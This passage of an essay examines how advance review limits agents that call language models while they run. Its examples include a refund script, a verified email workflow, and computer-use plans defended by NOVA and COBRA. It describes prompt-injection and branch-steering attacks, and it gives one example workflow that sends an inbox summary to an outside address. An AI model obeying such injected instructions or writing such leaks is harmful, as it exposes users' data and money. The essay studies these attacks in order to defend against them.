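# Plans That Call Language Models While They Run: What Advance Review Approves

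## What a reviewer reads and what is decided during the run

An AI agent is a language model that can act through tools, such as an email account, a payment system or a command line. In many agents, the model picks an action, receives the result and then picks the next action. Others first write out the whole job as a short computer program, which a person or an automatic checker reads before any of it runs. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) calls this arrangement code-then-execute and illustrates it with a three-line program for a user who wants to email the day's schedule to a boss. The program reads the calendar, asks a language model to format the entries, and emails the model's answer to the boss's address. A reviewer can read every line and still not know what the email will contain, because the model writes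 it during the run.

At least one company, Imprint, already works this way on small internal jobs. *Building an internal agent*, an engineer's account of automation there, describes the job of marking finished code changes in a chat channel where colleagues post them for review. At first a language model did the whole job from a prompt, but it sometimes marked unfinished changes, which nobody then reviewed. So the engineers moved the job into a Python script that can call a model where that helps. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, could almost always turn such a prompt into a script at the first attempt, and the scripts go through ordinary code review.

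Designers put a review between planning and execution because a check during the run may come too late. In *Guardians of the Agents*, Meijer describes a monitor that stops an agent from leaking private emails, but only after the agent has read them. Eric Drexler gives a broader reason for the review in his open agency model, where generative models only propose plans, independent critics help select one, and separate agents carry it out within a budget and a schedule. With the work divided this way, nobody has to hand a consequential task to a single opaque system whose plans are hidden.

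Drexler's scheme depends on plans that people and other programs can inspect from outside. A program that calls a language model while it runs only partly meets that condition. Drexler also notes that one very capable model could fill several of the scheme's separate roles. In a code-then-execute system, the same model might write the program and, after the review, answer the program's queries.

### The refund script

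A plan's *scaffold* consists of the steps, loops, conditions, prompts and limits that exist before review. A *runtime model call* is a point in the run where the plan sends a request to a language model and uses the answer. A *deferred decision* is a choice made during the run, after review, that affects what the plan does.

In the calendar program, the recipient is part of the scaffold and the wording of the message is a deferred decision. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which defines a small formal language for agents, has an example of the reverse, in which the program fixes an email's subject and body and a runtime model call extracts the recipient's address from an incoming message. Someone who plants instructions in that message cannot change the email's subject or body, but may be able to change who receives it. A reviewer who knew only that each program contained one model call would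 miss this difference.

Money makes the stakes easier to count. Suppose a support agent submits this plan:

```
for t in next_tickets(at_most=20):
    answer = ask_model("How many dollars should we refund?", t.text)
    if is_whole_number(answer) and 0 <= answer <= 50:
        pay(t.customer, answer)
    else:
        leave_open(t)
```

The script takes up to 20 support tickets and sends the text of each to a model. If the model answers with a whole number of dollars from 0 to 50, the script pays that amount to the customer who opened the ticket. It rejects any other answer and leaves the ticket open.

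The condition in the third line gives the model's answer a *type*, meaning a declared kind of value that a checker can enforce, such as a yes/no answer or a list of integers. The test happens during the run, so the reviewer confirms in advance only that it is on the sole path to `pay`. Meijer describes the same split in Java, which verifies much of a program before it starts and still checks every array index while it runs.

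With the type in place, the reviewer can work out the worst case without knowing anything about the model. The loop runs at most 20 times, each pass makes at most one payment, and no payment exceeds $50, so at most 20 × $50 = $1,000 leaves the account. This assumes the tools do what their names suggest. If `pay` retries after a timeout when the first attempt had gone through, a single ticket can cost $100. The reviewer therefore has to read `pay` as well, or trust somebody who has.

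*Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a survey of ways to specify and check what agents do, defines a plan as a finite sequence of actions, π = (a₁, …, aₙ), and writes π ⊨ φ when the plan satisfies a safety property φ. The refund script allows many such sequences. A *permitted run* is any sequence of actions the scaffold allows, given some possible set of model answers and outside data, and R is the set of all permitted runs. A property φ is a *guaranteed property* of the script when π ⊨ φ for every π in R, in which case the review has settled it. The $1,000 limit and the rule that nobody without a ticket receives a refund are both guaranteed properties.

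Advance review leaves open who gets the money. The names come from whatever tickets are waiting when the script starts, and the model's answers divide the sum among them. Even for a known set of 20 tickets there are 51²⁰, or about 1.4 × 10³⁴, possible lists of answers, although this count is a poor measure of how much is at stake. If 20 people write in about broken kettles and one of them never bought a kettle, the plan permits a run that pays $50 to each of the nineteen real buyers and nothing to the twentieth person. It also permits a run that pays the full $50 to the twentieth person and nothing to the buyers.

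The model might misjudge the tickets. It might also meet a *prompt injection*, which is text in the data it reads that it obeys as an instruction. For example, a customer could end a complaint by writing that company policy requires an answer of 50 on this ticket. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) introduced a benchmark of the same name that measures how tool-using agents cope with such attacks. It gives them ordinary jobs in simulated email, chat, travel and banking systems, with hostile instructions planted in the data. The benchmark started with 629 test cases and now has more than 900, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026).

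An injection in one ticket can gain the attacker at most $50 from the refund script, the same amount a customer could get with a plausible false story. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues make this point about a program that asks a model, file by file, whether each file is an invoice. An injection can get a malicious file counted as an invoice, but a real invoice would have been counted too. The harm is limited in this way only if the model reads one ticket per call. If the script put all 20 tickets into a single request for 20 numbers, an injection in one could raise or lower the refunds of the others. The $1,000 limit would still hold, but it would not ensure fairness among the customers. In either version, an attacker who opens all 20 tickets can get the whole $1,000 in a run that the scaffold permits.

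### Three changes to the script

If the model instead chooses one of four answers rather than naming a sum, the script contains a branch for each: refuse, pay $20, pay $50, or leave the ticket for a member of staff. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues compare a model in this position to a "switch" statement, which selects one of several listed pieces of code to run. The $1,000 limit still holds, because the reviewer can read all four branches and see that the largest payment is $50 per ticket. The number of branches doesn't set this limit. If the author replaces "pay $50" with "refund the full purchase price", the model still has only four possible answers, but the sum at risk now depends on what the 20 customers bought.

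A larger change is to give the model the refund tool. For each ticket, the script launches an agent with the customer's text, an instruction to resolve the complaint and permission to call `pay`. The loop still runs at most 20 times, but this now limits the number of agents rather than the number of payments. Neither guaranteed property holds any longer, because an agent can pay twice, pay $400 or pay somebody who has no ticket. Adding "never refund more than $50" to the prompt does not restore the guarantees, because large refunds become less likely but are still permitted. This design is not unusual. Scripts at Imprint can call a subagent with full access to tools, and the workflow scripts in Claude Code are mainly used to launch agents.

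The limit can come back from outside the script, if the tool or the account enforces it. Amazon's cloud division sells a system for this. AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) describes rules that sit apart from the agent's code, at a gateway that checks every tool call and blocks those the rules do not allow. The worked example in AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* happens to be a refund tool. Only one named user may issue refunds, each has to stay under a ceiling, and the gateway denies whatever no rule permits. (The page gives the requirement as $500 or less, while the rule tests for less than 500, so a refund of exactly $500 would fail. A reviewer who read only the English would have approved something slightly different from what runs.)

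A limit on each payment does not limit the total. If the gateway allows $50 a payment, an agent that calls the tool 100 times can spend $5,000 with every call within the limit. Dantas and colleagues found a similar gap in the research they surveyed, where monitoring during the run is the most mature way to enforce safety but its guarantees cover only single steps or short stretches. To restore the $1,000 limit, the gateway has to track earlier payments. AWS's *Temporal policies* documents rules that can do this by counting or summing earlier actions and refusing any action that would cross a threshold. These rules look back 24 hours at most, and only within one session, whose identifier the caller supplies. A new session restarts the count from zero. The limit therefore holds for the refund script if the job finishes within a day and the model cannot open a new session. A simpler way to enforce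 the limit is to use a dedicated account with $1,000 in it and no overdraft.

In the last variant, the model returns code and the script executes it. The reviewer reads an instruction to run code that does not exist yet. Unless something confines it, the generated code can do whatever the surrounding script can do, including calling `pay` in a loop, fetching more tickets, or overwriting the function that checks the amount. Safeguards that worked when the model could only call the tool may now fail. For example, if the script's author wrapped `pay` in a few lines that keep a running total, code running in the same process may be able to bypass them. The generated code can also bypass the gateway's session total if it can send requests under a new session identifier. The dedicated account still limits spending, provided the script has no credentials for any other account, but it doesn't prevent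 other kinds of harm. The generated code could still send the customer list to a stranger.

### Two readings of "approved"

The reviewer signs the original script, with its range check, expecting from past experience that refunds will total about $200. During the run, the model returns 50 for every ticket, and the script pays out $1,000. Did the reviewer approve the $1,000 payout?

The approval authorises this run if it covers every run the plan permits, which can be called the every-run reading. The expected-run reading limits the approval to the runs the reviewer had in mind, and this was not one of them.

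Anyone can apply the every-run reading by looking at the program. This reading also makes approving a plan worthwhile, because if approval covered only what the reviewer expected, the program would have to stop for permission at every surprise. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) describes a research system, ACE, that replaces step-by-step permission prompts with a single decision over an abstract plan. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) argues that a new tool call need not require a new approval if it stays within the scope of a decision the user has already approved. OpenAI's *Model Spec* (2025), an earlier version of the company's public description of how its models should behave, also treats authority as a boundary agreed in advance. It calls for a scope of autonomy that covers the permitted sub-goals, the acceptable costs and the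 points at which the model must pause, and it suggests recording the scope in fields such as a list of allowed tools and a maximum cost. The model must stay within that scope even where leaving it would seem to serve the user.

A further problem is that somebody has to guess these expectations while the program runs, and that will probably be a model. Mowshowitz (2026), in *OpenAI Updates Its Model Spec*, quotes a passage from the October 2026 version which says that a model may help users reflect but should not treat its prediction of what they would eventually decide as a decision they have made.

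Still, no reviewer pictures 10³⁴ lists of refunds before signing, so the every-run reading assumes a lot about what the reviewer considered. People approve overreaching actions even when a prompt shows them each one. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026) reports an experiment in which participants in the human-in-the-loop condition approved 96 of the 238 overreaching actions (40%) that permission prompts showed them. A program that contains a loop and a model call is probably harder to picture than the single actions in those prompts, so a signature on it is weaker evidence of what the signer wanted.

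OpenAI's documents also support this side. The 2025 version of the Model Spec tells models to respect the spirit of an instruction as well as its letter, and gives as an example of failure an assistant that deletes all the files when told to "clean up my desktop". *An updated Model Spec for more capable and beneficial AI*, OpenAI's announcement of the 2026 version, calls for good judgment in situations that instructions do not explicitly address, and a run that nobody foresaw is such a situation.

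Facts can also change between the signature and the payment. For example, the customer's bank might return the money overnight, and the script would then pay the refund again in the morning. In *Runtime Control for AI Agents*, Bhadane, Yerramsetti and colleagues (2026) argue that an approval may stop authorising an action once the facts behind it have changed. They built a layer that ties each approval to those facts and checks them again just before acting. In a replay of 42 scripted cases, it caught 15 approvals that later events had invalidated, held back 14 of the actions and compensated for one that had already taken effect. The comparison system was designed never to re-check anything, so the result shows that a re-check can work but doesn't measure how often real approvals become invalid.

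Expectations are perhaps less vague in practice than one would fear, at least when they are applied after the run. *Act on Your Behalf, Beyond Your Authorization* (2026) presents a benchmark of agents that exceed their permissions. A human annotator and an AI judge labelled 100 records of agents at work and agreed on 97 about whether the agent had overstepped. In one of the three disputed cases, the agent had permission to send a musician's performance dates and also sent the venue, the city and the ticket tier. But the benchmark specified in advance what would count as overstepping, and the judges could see what the agent had done, while a reviewer with an unwritten expectation has neither advantage.

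In the refund example, suppose a run pays out the $200 the reviewer expected, but $50 of it goes to the customer who planted an instruction in the ticket. The every-run reading counts this as authorised but the expected-run reading does not, and an alarm on the total would not have caught it. If the model has an unrestricted refund tool, the every-run reading implies that the reviewer has authorised emptying the account. Few reviewers would accept that they had approved this, which seems a good reason to apply the reading before signing, since it would lead them to refuse the plan or demand a limit. The expected-run reading also fails for generated code, because the reviewer has no code from which to form an expectation.

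The every-run reading looks safer for deciding whether to approve a plan. The expected-run reading is better for identifying afterwards that something went wrong, even when every line of the program worked correctly. Authors can bring the two readings closer together by writing expectations into the scaffold. A reviewer who expects a total of about $200 can ask for a line that stops the script and calls a person before the total passes $300. The reviewer also expects the money to go to people with a genuine complaint, but no line of code can check for that, which is why the script needs the model.

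## An email workflow with one model call, verified before it runs

In the refund script, each of the model's answers can move money. The central workflow in Meijer's *Guardians of the Agents* also contains one model call, but the answer goes only to the person who asked for it. Meijer proposes that an agent's model write out the whole job as a workflow before it reads any data, and that the workflow run only if it passes a separate program's check against a security policy.

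Meijer first shows what can happen without this safeguard. A user called Michelle asks an agent to fetch and summarise her emails. The agent has separate tools for fetching and sending mail. One message in the inbox contains an instruction to send a summary of the mailbox to an outside address, supposedly for legal compliance, without asking for confirmation or mentioning it. The agent follows the instruction, then shows Michelle a summary of the other four messages.

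Under the proposal, the model has only Michelle's request and a description of the tools when it writes the workflow. Each step names a tool, its inputs, a label for the result and the step that follows. Meijer uses JSON, a text format for structured data, but the workflow comes to three lines of ordinary code:

```
emails_fetched = fetch_mail()
email_summary  = summarize_emails(emails_fetched)
return email_summary
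```

The name `emails_fetched` stands for messages that nobody has fetched yet. An interpreter fills in the real messages during the run and carries out the three steps in order. The list of steps is already complete when the malicious email arrives.

The second step calls a language model at runtime. Meijer implements `summarize_emails` as a short prompt that asks the model for a bullet-point list, with suspicious messages and spam marked as such. The malicious email still reaches a model, but this model takes and returns text and has no tool for sending mail. If a developer later gave the summariser such a tool, Michelle would lose the protection even though the three lines would look the same. A reviewer therefore has to look inside `summarize_emails` for the same reason as inside `pay`.

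### How a checker finds a leak

Writing the workflow before reading the mail doesn't help if the workflow is bad from the start. The model reads the tool descriptions first, and somebody could hide an instruction there, for example that company rules require a copy of every summary to go to an outside address. A malicious user could put the same demand in the request. The model might then write this:

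```
emails_fetched = fetch_mail()
email_summary  = summarize_emails(emails_fetched)
send_email(to="someone@outside.example", body=email_summary)
return email_summary
```

Meijer's remedy is a source-and-sink policy. A source is a point where sensitive data enters the workflow, and a sink is a tool input that the data must not reach. Here the source is the result of fetching mail, and the sink is the body of any email sent to an address outside the company's domain, valleysharks.com.

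The checker works on the text of the workflow, without fetching any emails. It marks `emails_fetched` as mail contents. The summariser takes a marked input, so the checker marks `email_summary` too. The third line puts that summary into the body of an email to an outside address. This completes a path from source to sink, so the checker rejects the workflow. This technique is called taint analysis, and Meijer suggests running it with existing code-analysis tools such as CodeQL and Semgrep.

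The checker treats the summariser's output as mail contents whatever it says, even if it is a single word, so the method also rejects some harmless plans. If Michelle wanted the agent to look through her mail and tell an outside organiser whether she is free on Tuesday, the policy would block the answer because even a "yes" or "no" would count as mail contents.

A policy also covers only what its author wrote down. Meijer's policy names its source as `fetch_email`, but the JSON workflow calls `fetch_mail`, so a checker that compared names literally would find no source and raise no alarm. Meijer also gives an example of a subtler gap. A user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the model writes a workflow that deletes every text file. If the specification requires only that the two files be gone afterwards, this workflow satisfies it. The specification's author has to add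 a frame condition stating that everything else stays as it was.

### What Michelle can rely on

The three-line workflow has no send step, so an injected instruction cannot make it send an email. This follows from *control-flow integrity*, the property that the workflow executes only actions written in the plan. The property holds whatever the summariser outputs, as long as the interpreter and the tools do only what they are described as doing.

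Verifying the plan doesn't constrain what the summary says. The malicious email contains an instruction to leave it out of the summary, and the plan allows the summariser to follow it. The plan also allows a summary that wrongly says a meeting is cancelled, or one that gives Michelle an attacker's bank details for a payment. In Meijer's sample output, the summariser flags the malicious email as suspicious, but it also marks as spam an invitation to an investors' forum, which the summary in the earlier example listed as an ordinary message. If Michelle wanted to attend, no check on the workflow would catch the mistake.

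A stricter policy probably can't close this gap. Meijer (2026) argues in *I've never seen anything scarier than an LLM with tool calls* that an answer can't be formally proved safe, because "safe" is not a mathematical property of a text. For the summariser, Meijer recommends conventional guardrails, which filter a model's inputs and outputs, but elsewhere criticises them for raising false alarms and acting too late. The one step where a model reads hostile text therefore gets the kind of protection Meijer trusts least.

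In the talk, Meijer also says that words are harmless until a person acts on them, but people usually ask for a summary to act on it. A summary could also do harm without anyone acting on it. If the program that displays it automatically loads images from web addresses in the text, a crafted address could carry mail contents to an attacker. A careful policy would then treat the return step as a sink too.

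### Adding a step that acts on the summary

Suppose Michelle also wants to send the summary to her assistant at the same company. The model adds one `send_email` line with the assistant's address, and the policy allows it because the address is internal. No permitted run can send the summary to an outside address, as before. But the author of the malicious email can now influence a message that comes from Michelle's account, and an assistant is more likely to pay an invoice if the request comes from her than from a stranger. Meijer's policy tracks private data leaving the company. Keeping hostile text out of Michelle's messages would require another rule, with outside mail as the source and any message sent in her name as the sink. That rule would forbid forwarding the summary at all.

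If the workflow replies to everyone who asked for a meeting, it reads the addresses from the inbox during the run, so the checker cannot verify in advance whether they are internal. The checker must either reject the plan or require a test immediately before each send, like the range check in the refund script.

Michelle might instead ask the agent to delete whatever the summariser marks as spam. The source-and-sink policy would allow this, since the workflow sends nothing. The model's labels would then determine which messages are deleted, including the forum invitation in Meijer's sample output. As with 20 tickets in one request, an instruction in one message could change the labels on the others. Moving the messages to a folder would make mistakes reversible, and a cap of ten deletions a day would limit the damage. Either change would protect Michelle better than a more precise leak policy.

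### Asking or monitoring instead

Meijer compares permission prompts at every tool call to cookie banners. When security questions interrupt their work, people get used to clicking "Allow", as the earlier experiment with permission prompts also suggests. People also get distracted from supervising the agent closely. According to AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), a write-up of the same talk, Claude Code blanked one of Meijer's source files while Meijer was preparing the slides.

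Reviewing an agent's logs finds a leak only after it has happened, while a live monitor can stop it beforehand. Meijer's monitor is a security automaton, a small state machine that changes state with each tool call and stops the agent when it reaches an error state. The objection that it acts only after the agent has read private mail seems weak in this example, because Michelle asked for her mail to be read, the verified workflow reads it too, and the attacker gets nothing if the monitor blocks the send call before it executes.

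The case for checking first is stronger when a job has several irreversible steps. ClauZ3's *Background And Related Work*, from the documentation for a tool that checks agents' Python programs before they run, notes that a monitor may refuse the second action after the first has taken effect. An agent might cancel a flight and then find that it isn't allowed to buy the replacement. A check in advance would reject both actions together. Meijer concludes that verification removes the need for rollbacks, but it does so only for rollbacks that a policy violation would have caused. The airline's website can still go down between the cancellation and the purchase.

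### Tasks that depend on what the data contains

The scheme assumes that a model can write the plan before it reads the data, and for many tasks it can't. If Michelle asks an agent to deal with whatever came in this morning, the right steps depend on whether the senders want a signature, a date or a refund. In programming, too, an error message often determines which file to open next. ClauZ3's *Guardians Synergies*, a design note on combining the two approaches, leaves open whether planning before the data arrives suits coding agents, and leans towards offering it as an option. Meijer expects that planning in code helps models reason, but concedes that nobody has formally measured how it affects their ability to answer users' requests.

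A workflow can include branches and loops for cases that somebody foresaw, such as meeting requests, but these won't cover an unexpected kind of message. The agent could instead plan in rounds, reading the mail and then writing a second workflow, which is also checked before it runs. But the model that writes the second workflow has read the attacker's text, so the attacker can in effect propose steps for it. In the original scheme, an attacker's email could not add a send step, even if the policy allowed one. With a second round, it can add any step that the policy doesn't forbid, so security depends much more on whether somebody thought of the right rule.

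### The Guardians verifier and later work

Meijer's article describes the verifier but doesn't supply a finished one. There is now an open-source implementation called Guardians, which the Harvard computer scientist Nada Amin lists under static verification of workflows on her SEAS project page, *Topics of GitHub Projects*. As ClauZ3 describes it, Guardians labels each value with its origin and follows the labels through the workflow. It also accepts sanitisers, steps that a policy treats as making data safe to pass on. Declaring the summariser a sanitiser would remove the protection against the leak above. Guardians can also run a security automaton over the planned steps in advance, so a policy can require, for example, an approval before any transfer.

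A bug in the checker could let a bad plan through. Midspiral's *LemmaScript (Tech Preview)* describes a machine-checked proof that the core method is sound, meaning that if the checker passes a workflow, no path through it leaks marked data to a sink or puts the automaton into an error state. The proof covers branches, where the checker combines the marks from both sides, and loops, where it combines the marks a value has at the start with those added in one pass. The proof shows that this is enough for any number of passes. It applies to a TypeScript version of the method, whose agreement with the Python original has only been tested. An unverified adapter connects the TypeScript version to Guardians-style workflows.

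Other developers have applied similar checks to workflows that already exist. *Agentproof* extracts the graph of steps from agents built with four common frameworks, including LangGraph and CrewAI, and checks it before deployment, so nobody has to model the workflow by hand.

Meijer's 2026 talks are stricter than the article. In *Return of the Theorem* (2026), Meijer argues that people should treat agents as guilty until proven innocent, and proposes writing business rules as logical clauses that a solver can check plans against. In the World's Fair talk, the model has to supply a proof with its plan, an idea Meijer credits to the proof-carrying code of the 1990s. The write-up illustrates this with a small planning language that can read files, delete files and finish with an answer. Its proof rules for "deletes nothing" cover reading and finishing but not deleting, so no plan that contains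 a deletion can have a valid proof. If a plan reads a file, the proof has to hold for any contents the file might have. AI Engineer notes that the proof would still be worthless if the interpreter deleted files while reading them.

In ClauZ3, the agent writes a Python program and proposes guarantees about it, such as that it emails nobody but Bob or spends no more than $500 in total. A prover checks the guarantees against every branch, and the user approves them instead of the code, which they don't have to read. This is close to the every-run reading of approval. The agent can propose a weak guarantee, but the user can see that it is weak and ask for a stronger one. With a list of permitted recipients, ClauZ3 would reject the plan that sends Michelle's summary to an outside address. It cannot yet express a rule that keeps the contents of her inbox out of an email to somebody on the list.

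## Computer-use plans in which a model picks the branch

Michelle's workflow could have a fixed order of steps because its author knew what kind of result each tool would return. A computer-use agent works without such tools, looking at screenshots of an ordinary desktop or web page and acting by clicking and typing. The next click depends on whether the browser is open, whether a notice covers the page and where the search box is, so most of these agents take a new screenshot before every action. Any hostile text on the screen then reaches the model that chooses the next action.

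*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) found that a model can often write the whole plan without seeing the screen if the plan has enough branches. The paper's system divides the work between two models. A planner receives only the user's request, its standing instructions and a list of functions, and writes a complete program. An ordinary software interpreter runs the program, and a second model reads the screen to answer the program's queries. This second model supplies values to the program but can't add a step to it, however persuasive the text on the screen is. The software developer Simon Willison proposed this division in 2023, and a system called CaMeL later applied it to agents with conventional tools such as email and calendars.

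### Observe, verify, act

The planning method, NOVA (Navigating via Observation, Verification, and Action), consists largely of advice in the planner's instructions, which Foerster and colleagues developed by studying successful plans. When the right action depends on the screen, the plan first observes by getting a short description of the screen from the screen-reading model. It then verifies with a function called `verify_hypothesis`, which takes the description and a prediction that the planner wrote in advance, such as "We are viewing a website". A language model compares the two texts and returns yes or no, and the interpreter takes the branch written for that answer. The plan acts only after this check, for example by getting the coordinates of a search box and clicking there.

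A plan for buying a water filter might include these lines, with the functions simplified:

```
view = describe_screen("What does the water filter cost?")
if verify_hypothesis(view, "The filter costs $50 or less"):
    click(find("the button that places the order"))
else:
    click(find("the button that saves the item for later"))
```

The planner writes all of this before anyone has looked up the price. During the run, models supply a description, a yes or no that determines whether the user buys something, and the position of a button.

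Describing the model's answer as yes or no is a slight simplification, because `verify_hypothesis` can return OK, FAIL or UNKNOWN in the paper's appendix and sample plans. One sample plan, written by GPT-5, treats UNKNOWN as a no when testing a prediction but as a success when a click returns it. If the click makes a payment, how the plan treats UNKNOWN would determine whether it tries again and perhaps pays twice.

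### Reading a plan with 40 branches

Foerster and colleagues compared 886 NOVA plans with 886 plans that a planner without NOVA's guidance wrote for the same tasks, and with 242 CaMeL plans for AgentDojo's office, travel and banking tasks.

| Average per plan | NOVA | Without NOVA's guidance | AgentDojo |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 213 | 72 | 52 |
| Tool calls | 41 | 20 | 5 |
| Branches | 40 | 11 | 4 |
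| Branches that depend on a model's answer | 24 | 8 | 2 |

Besides being shorter, the AgentDojo plans are easier to review because 79% of their branch conditions depend only on values inside the program, such as a loop counter, so a reader can work out what they will do. In NOVA plans, the share is 9%. The 24 tests that depend on a model could combine in as many as 16.8 million ways if each ran once and none depended on another, which is too many to review one by one.

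Roughly half the steps in a NOVA plan are fallbacks that a given run never reaches. A reviewer still has to read them, because nobody knows before the run which steps it will skip. Even for a programmer, 213 lines is a lot to read to approve one errand, and most people who would want the errand done are not programmers. Reading one plan also helps little with the next, because the paths through different NOVA plans for the same task overlap by only 0.04 on a scale from 0 to 1, compared with 0.39 on AgentDojo.

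A reviewer of the GPT-5 sample plan has to read three slightly different versions of the same routine for dismissing notices. If the planner called a shared function instead, a reviewer could approve the routine once and after that read only what is specific to each task.

A careful reader might also catch flaws in the sample plan. The task is to "browse the natural products database", and it starts with drugs.com open, which has a natural products category. The plan tests whether the screen shows a website, the desktop or an empty search page, and has a branch for each. If the site's own search finds nothing relevant, the plan searches the web and looks for links to other databases, three of which it names. Its final test accepts any natural products database with a browse or search page, so a run can end on the wrong website and report success, even with no attacker and no unapproved actions.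 Near the end, the plan also asks a model whether the task is finished, then marks it as done whatever the answer. Foerster and colleagues present this as an example of a good plan, and it probably is good compared with the others.

### What the plans achieve

Foerster and colleagues tested NOVA on OSWorld, a benchmark of 369 tasks in real applications such as Chrome, LibreOffice and the image editor GIMP. A script can mark most of the tasks. They first let Claude Sonnet 4.5, a leading model in late 2025, work in the usual way, with a new screenshot at each step, and it solved 109 of the tasks that a script could mark. They then tried NOVA on those 109 tasks, with Claude reading the screen. NOVA solved 31 of them (28%) at the first attempt and 62 (57%) in at least one of five attempts, each with a new plan. The headline result that NOVA retains up to 57% of the performance of frontier models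 uses the five-attempt figure.

The comparison favours NOVA in one way, because the ordinary agent had only one attempt at each task and at most 15 steps. (With 50 steps, its published score is 58.1% of the benchmark, against 37.7% here.) It disadvantages NOVA in another, because NOVA gets no credit for tasks that the ordinary agent failed. With 20 attempts, the share rises to about 73%. But extra attempts only help the user if somebody can tell which one worked, and anyone reviewing the plans in advance would have to read more than 1,000 lines for five of them.

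For UI-TARS, a small open model, the paper reports a relative improvement of up to 19%, from 24.4% to 29.0% of all tasks. The higher figure again allows several attempts, here three. On first attempts alone, NOVA completes about 22% of all tasks.

These figures would probably be higher with newer planners, because the choice of planner made a large difference. The best of nine planners solved 12 of 17 tasks and the worst solved four. The choice of screen-reading model mattered much less, with three very different models solving between 65% and 68% of the same 60 tasks within five attempts. With NOVA's guidance, the planner solved 35 of those 60 tasks within three attempts, but without it the planner wrote shorter programs that solved only 11, so the fallbacks that make a plan tiring to review are also a large part of why it works.

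Writing the full plan in advance seems to solve almost as many tasks as planning step by step under the same isolation. Foerster and colleagues also adapted Fides, a system in which the planner chooses one action at a time without seeing values from the screen. To make this work, they had to let the planner see the yes/no answers. The Fides version solved 40 of the 60 tasks, against 39 for full plans, but used many times more text. It also gives a reviewer no complete plan to read.

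### Approving the branches without approving the choice

Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, distinguish two properties a reviewer might want. The two-model design provides control-flow integrity, as Meijer's interpreter did for Michelle, because the agent can execute only actions in the approved plan. It does not provide *data-flow integrity*, the property that untrusted data cannot influence which approved branch runs or set the critical values of an action, such as the recipient of a payment.

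The reviewer approved ordering the water filter only if it cost $50 or less. Suppose it costs $400, but `verify_hypothesis` returns yes. The interpreter places the order, and control-flow integrity holds because every action was in the plan. The program can't test the price itself, only a model's output about the price. The plan therefore guarantees only that it won't reach the order button until a model has returned yes, which is much weaker than a limit on the price.

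The model might misread the page. It might also give the wrong answer because someone who controls part of the page, such as a seller or a person posting a review, wants a particular branch to run. Foerster and colleagues call this *branch steering*. The attacker doesn't need to add a new instruction, because the action they want is already in the plan the reviewer approved.

Control-flow integrity also guarantees less for computer use than it did in the mailbox example. A line that calls `send_email` can only send an email, but a line that clicks the position `find` returns might open a tab or confirm a bank transfer, depending on what is there. The reviewer approves the click and a description of its target, but the actual target is determined only when the plan runs.

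The plan still limits what an attacker can do. Foerster and colleagues argue that serious harm, such as a fraudulent transfer, would require a plan that already contains a step for submitting a payment, and at least two wrong answers that fit together. Sending the user to the wrong website or making the task fail takes only one wrong answer. They also tried having other models check the answers. One check caught six of ten attack runs and raised false alarms on four of 17 harmless tasks. Another, facing a harder attack, caught five of ten and raised false alarms on three of 17. Both checks seem to catch too few attacks to justify that many false alarms.

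Zingrillo and colleagues then built a benchmark, STEER-Bench, to measure the problem. Its 101 tasks cover nine domains and include bank transfers, warehouse logistics and changes to patients' doses. The tasks yield 199 attack cases, and ordinary computer-use agents can run 74 of them. On those 74, attacks succeeded 94.4% of the time against an ordinary agent that looks at the screen before each action. The two-model design, which separates the planner from the screen, lowered that rate only to 89.5%.

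The separation can still be useful despite this result, because the benchmark mostly targets weaknesses that the two-model design doesn't address. On 51 prompt-injection cases from an older benchmark, OS-Harm, the design blocked every attack without any further protection.

### How COBRA limits each branch

Zingrillo and colleagues propose a defence, COBRA, that attaches a set of permissions to each branch before the run starts. COBRA enforces these permissions on the messages that leave the computer, because a rule about clicks would be almost meaningless. *ceLLMate* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025), whose software COBRA adapts, gives the example of a rule that lets an agent click only at position (246, 1023). What is at that position depends on the website and the screen size. But when a click places an order, the browser has to send the shop's server a request that names the operation.

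COBRA needs a description of those operations, which Meng and colleagues call an agent sitemap. Each entry gives an operation's name, the form of the request and the fields it carries. For example, an entry for approving a loan could specify a request to `/loans/{id}/approve`. Tools that follow the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to outside services, already come with similar descriptions. The user approves each description once. COBRA stores a fingerprint of the approved text and asks for approval again if the text changes.

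The planner writes the program from the approved descriptions and the user's request. If the task requires a critical value that the user hasn't given and the plan has no authorised source for it, COBRA asks the user before the run. Ordinary code then lists the program's branches. In a separate call, the planner model, which has still received nothing from the screen, specifies which destinations, tools and field values each branch may use. The buying branch of the filter plan, for example, might permit only requests to the shop's own site, the operation that places an order, and a price of $50 or less.

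Each question about the screen has a declared answer type, such as a number for a price. During the run, the screen-reading model must either return a value of that type or report that it can't see one. The interpreter itself compares the price with $50. COBRA then inserts the observed values into the branch's constraints and checks every outgoing request and tool call against them. If the constraints permit a $40 order, COBRA blocks a request that contains a price of $80. A nested branch inherits the limits of the branches around it, and its own permissions expire when the run leaves it.

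COBRA blocked all 199 attacks in STEER-Bench. When Zingrillo and colleagues switched off the protection that each attack was meant to test, 87.6% of the attacks succeeded, so the cases were not simply too easy. COBRA kept 97% of the plain two-model system's success on harmless tasks and wrongly blocked legitimate actions in four of 138 harmless runs. However, the benchmark counts an attack as successful only when a harmful action violates the constraints in force at that point, so a harmful choice that the constraints permit would not count.

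The loss of ordinary usefulness is larger when COBRA is compared with an unprotected agent. On 361 tasks from OSWorld-MCP, a version of OSWorld with callable tools, Claude Sonnet 5 completed 51.0% as an ordinary agent and 38.8% when it filled both roles in COBRA, with up to five attempts per task. With GPT-5 as planner, a variant that merges five candidate plans into one program raised first-attempt successes from 78 to 105. A reviewer would also have one program to read instead of up to five, though it would presumably be longer.

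### What falls outside COBRA's boundary

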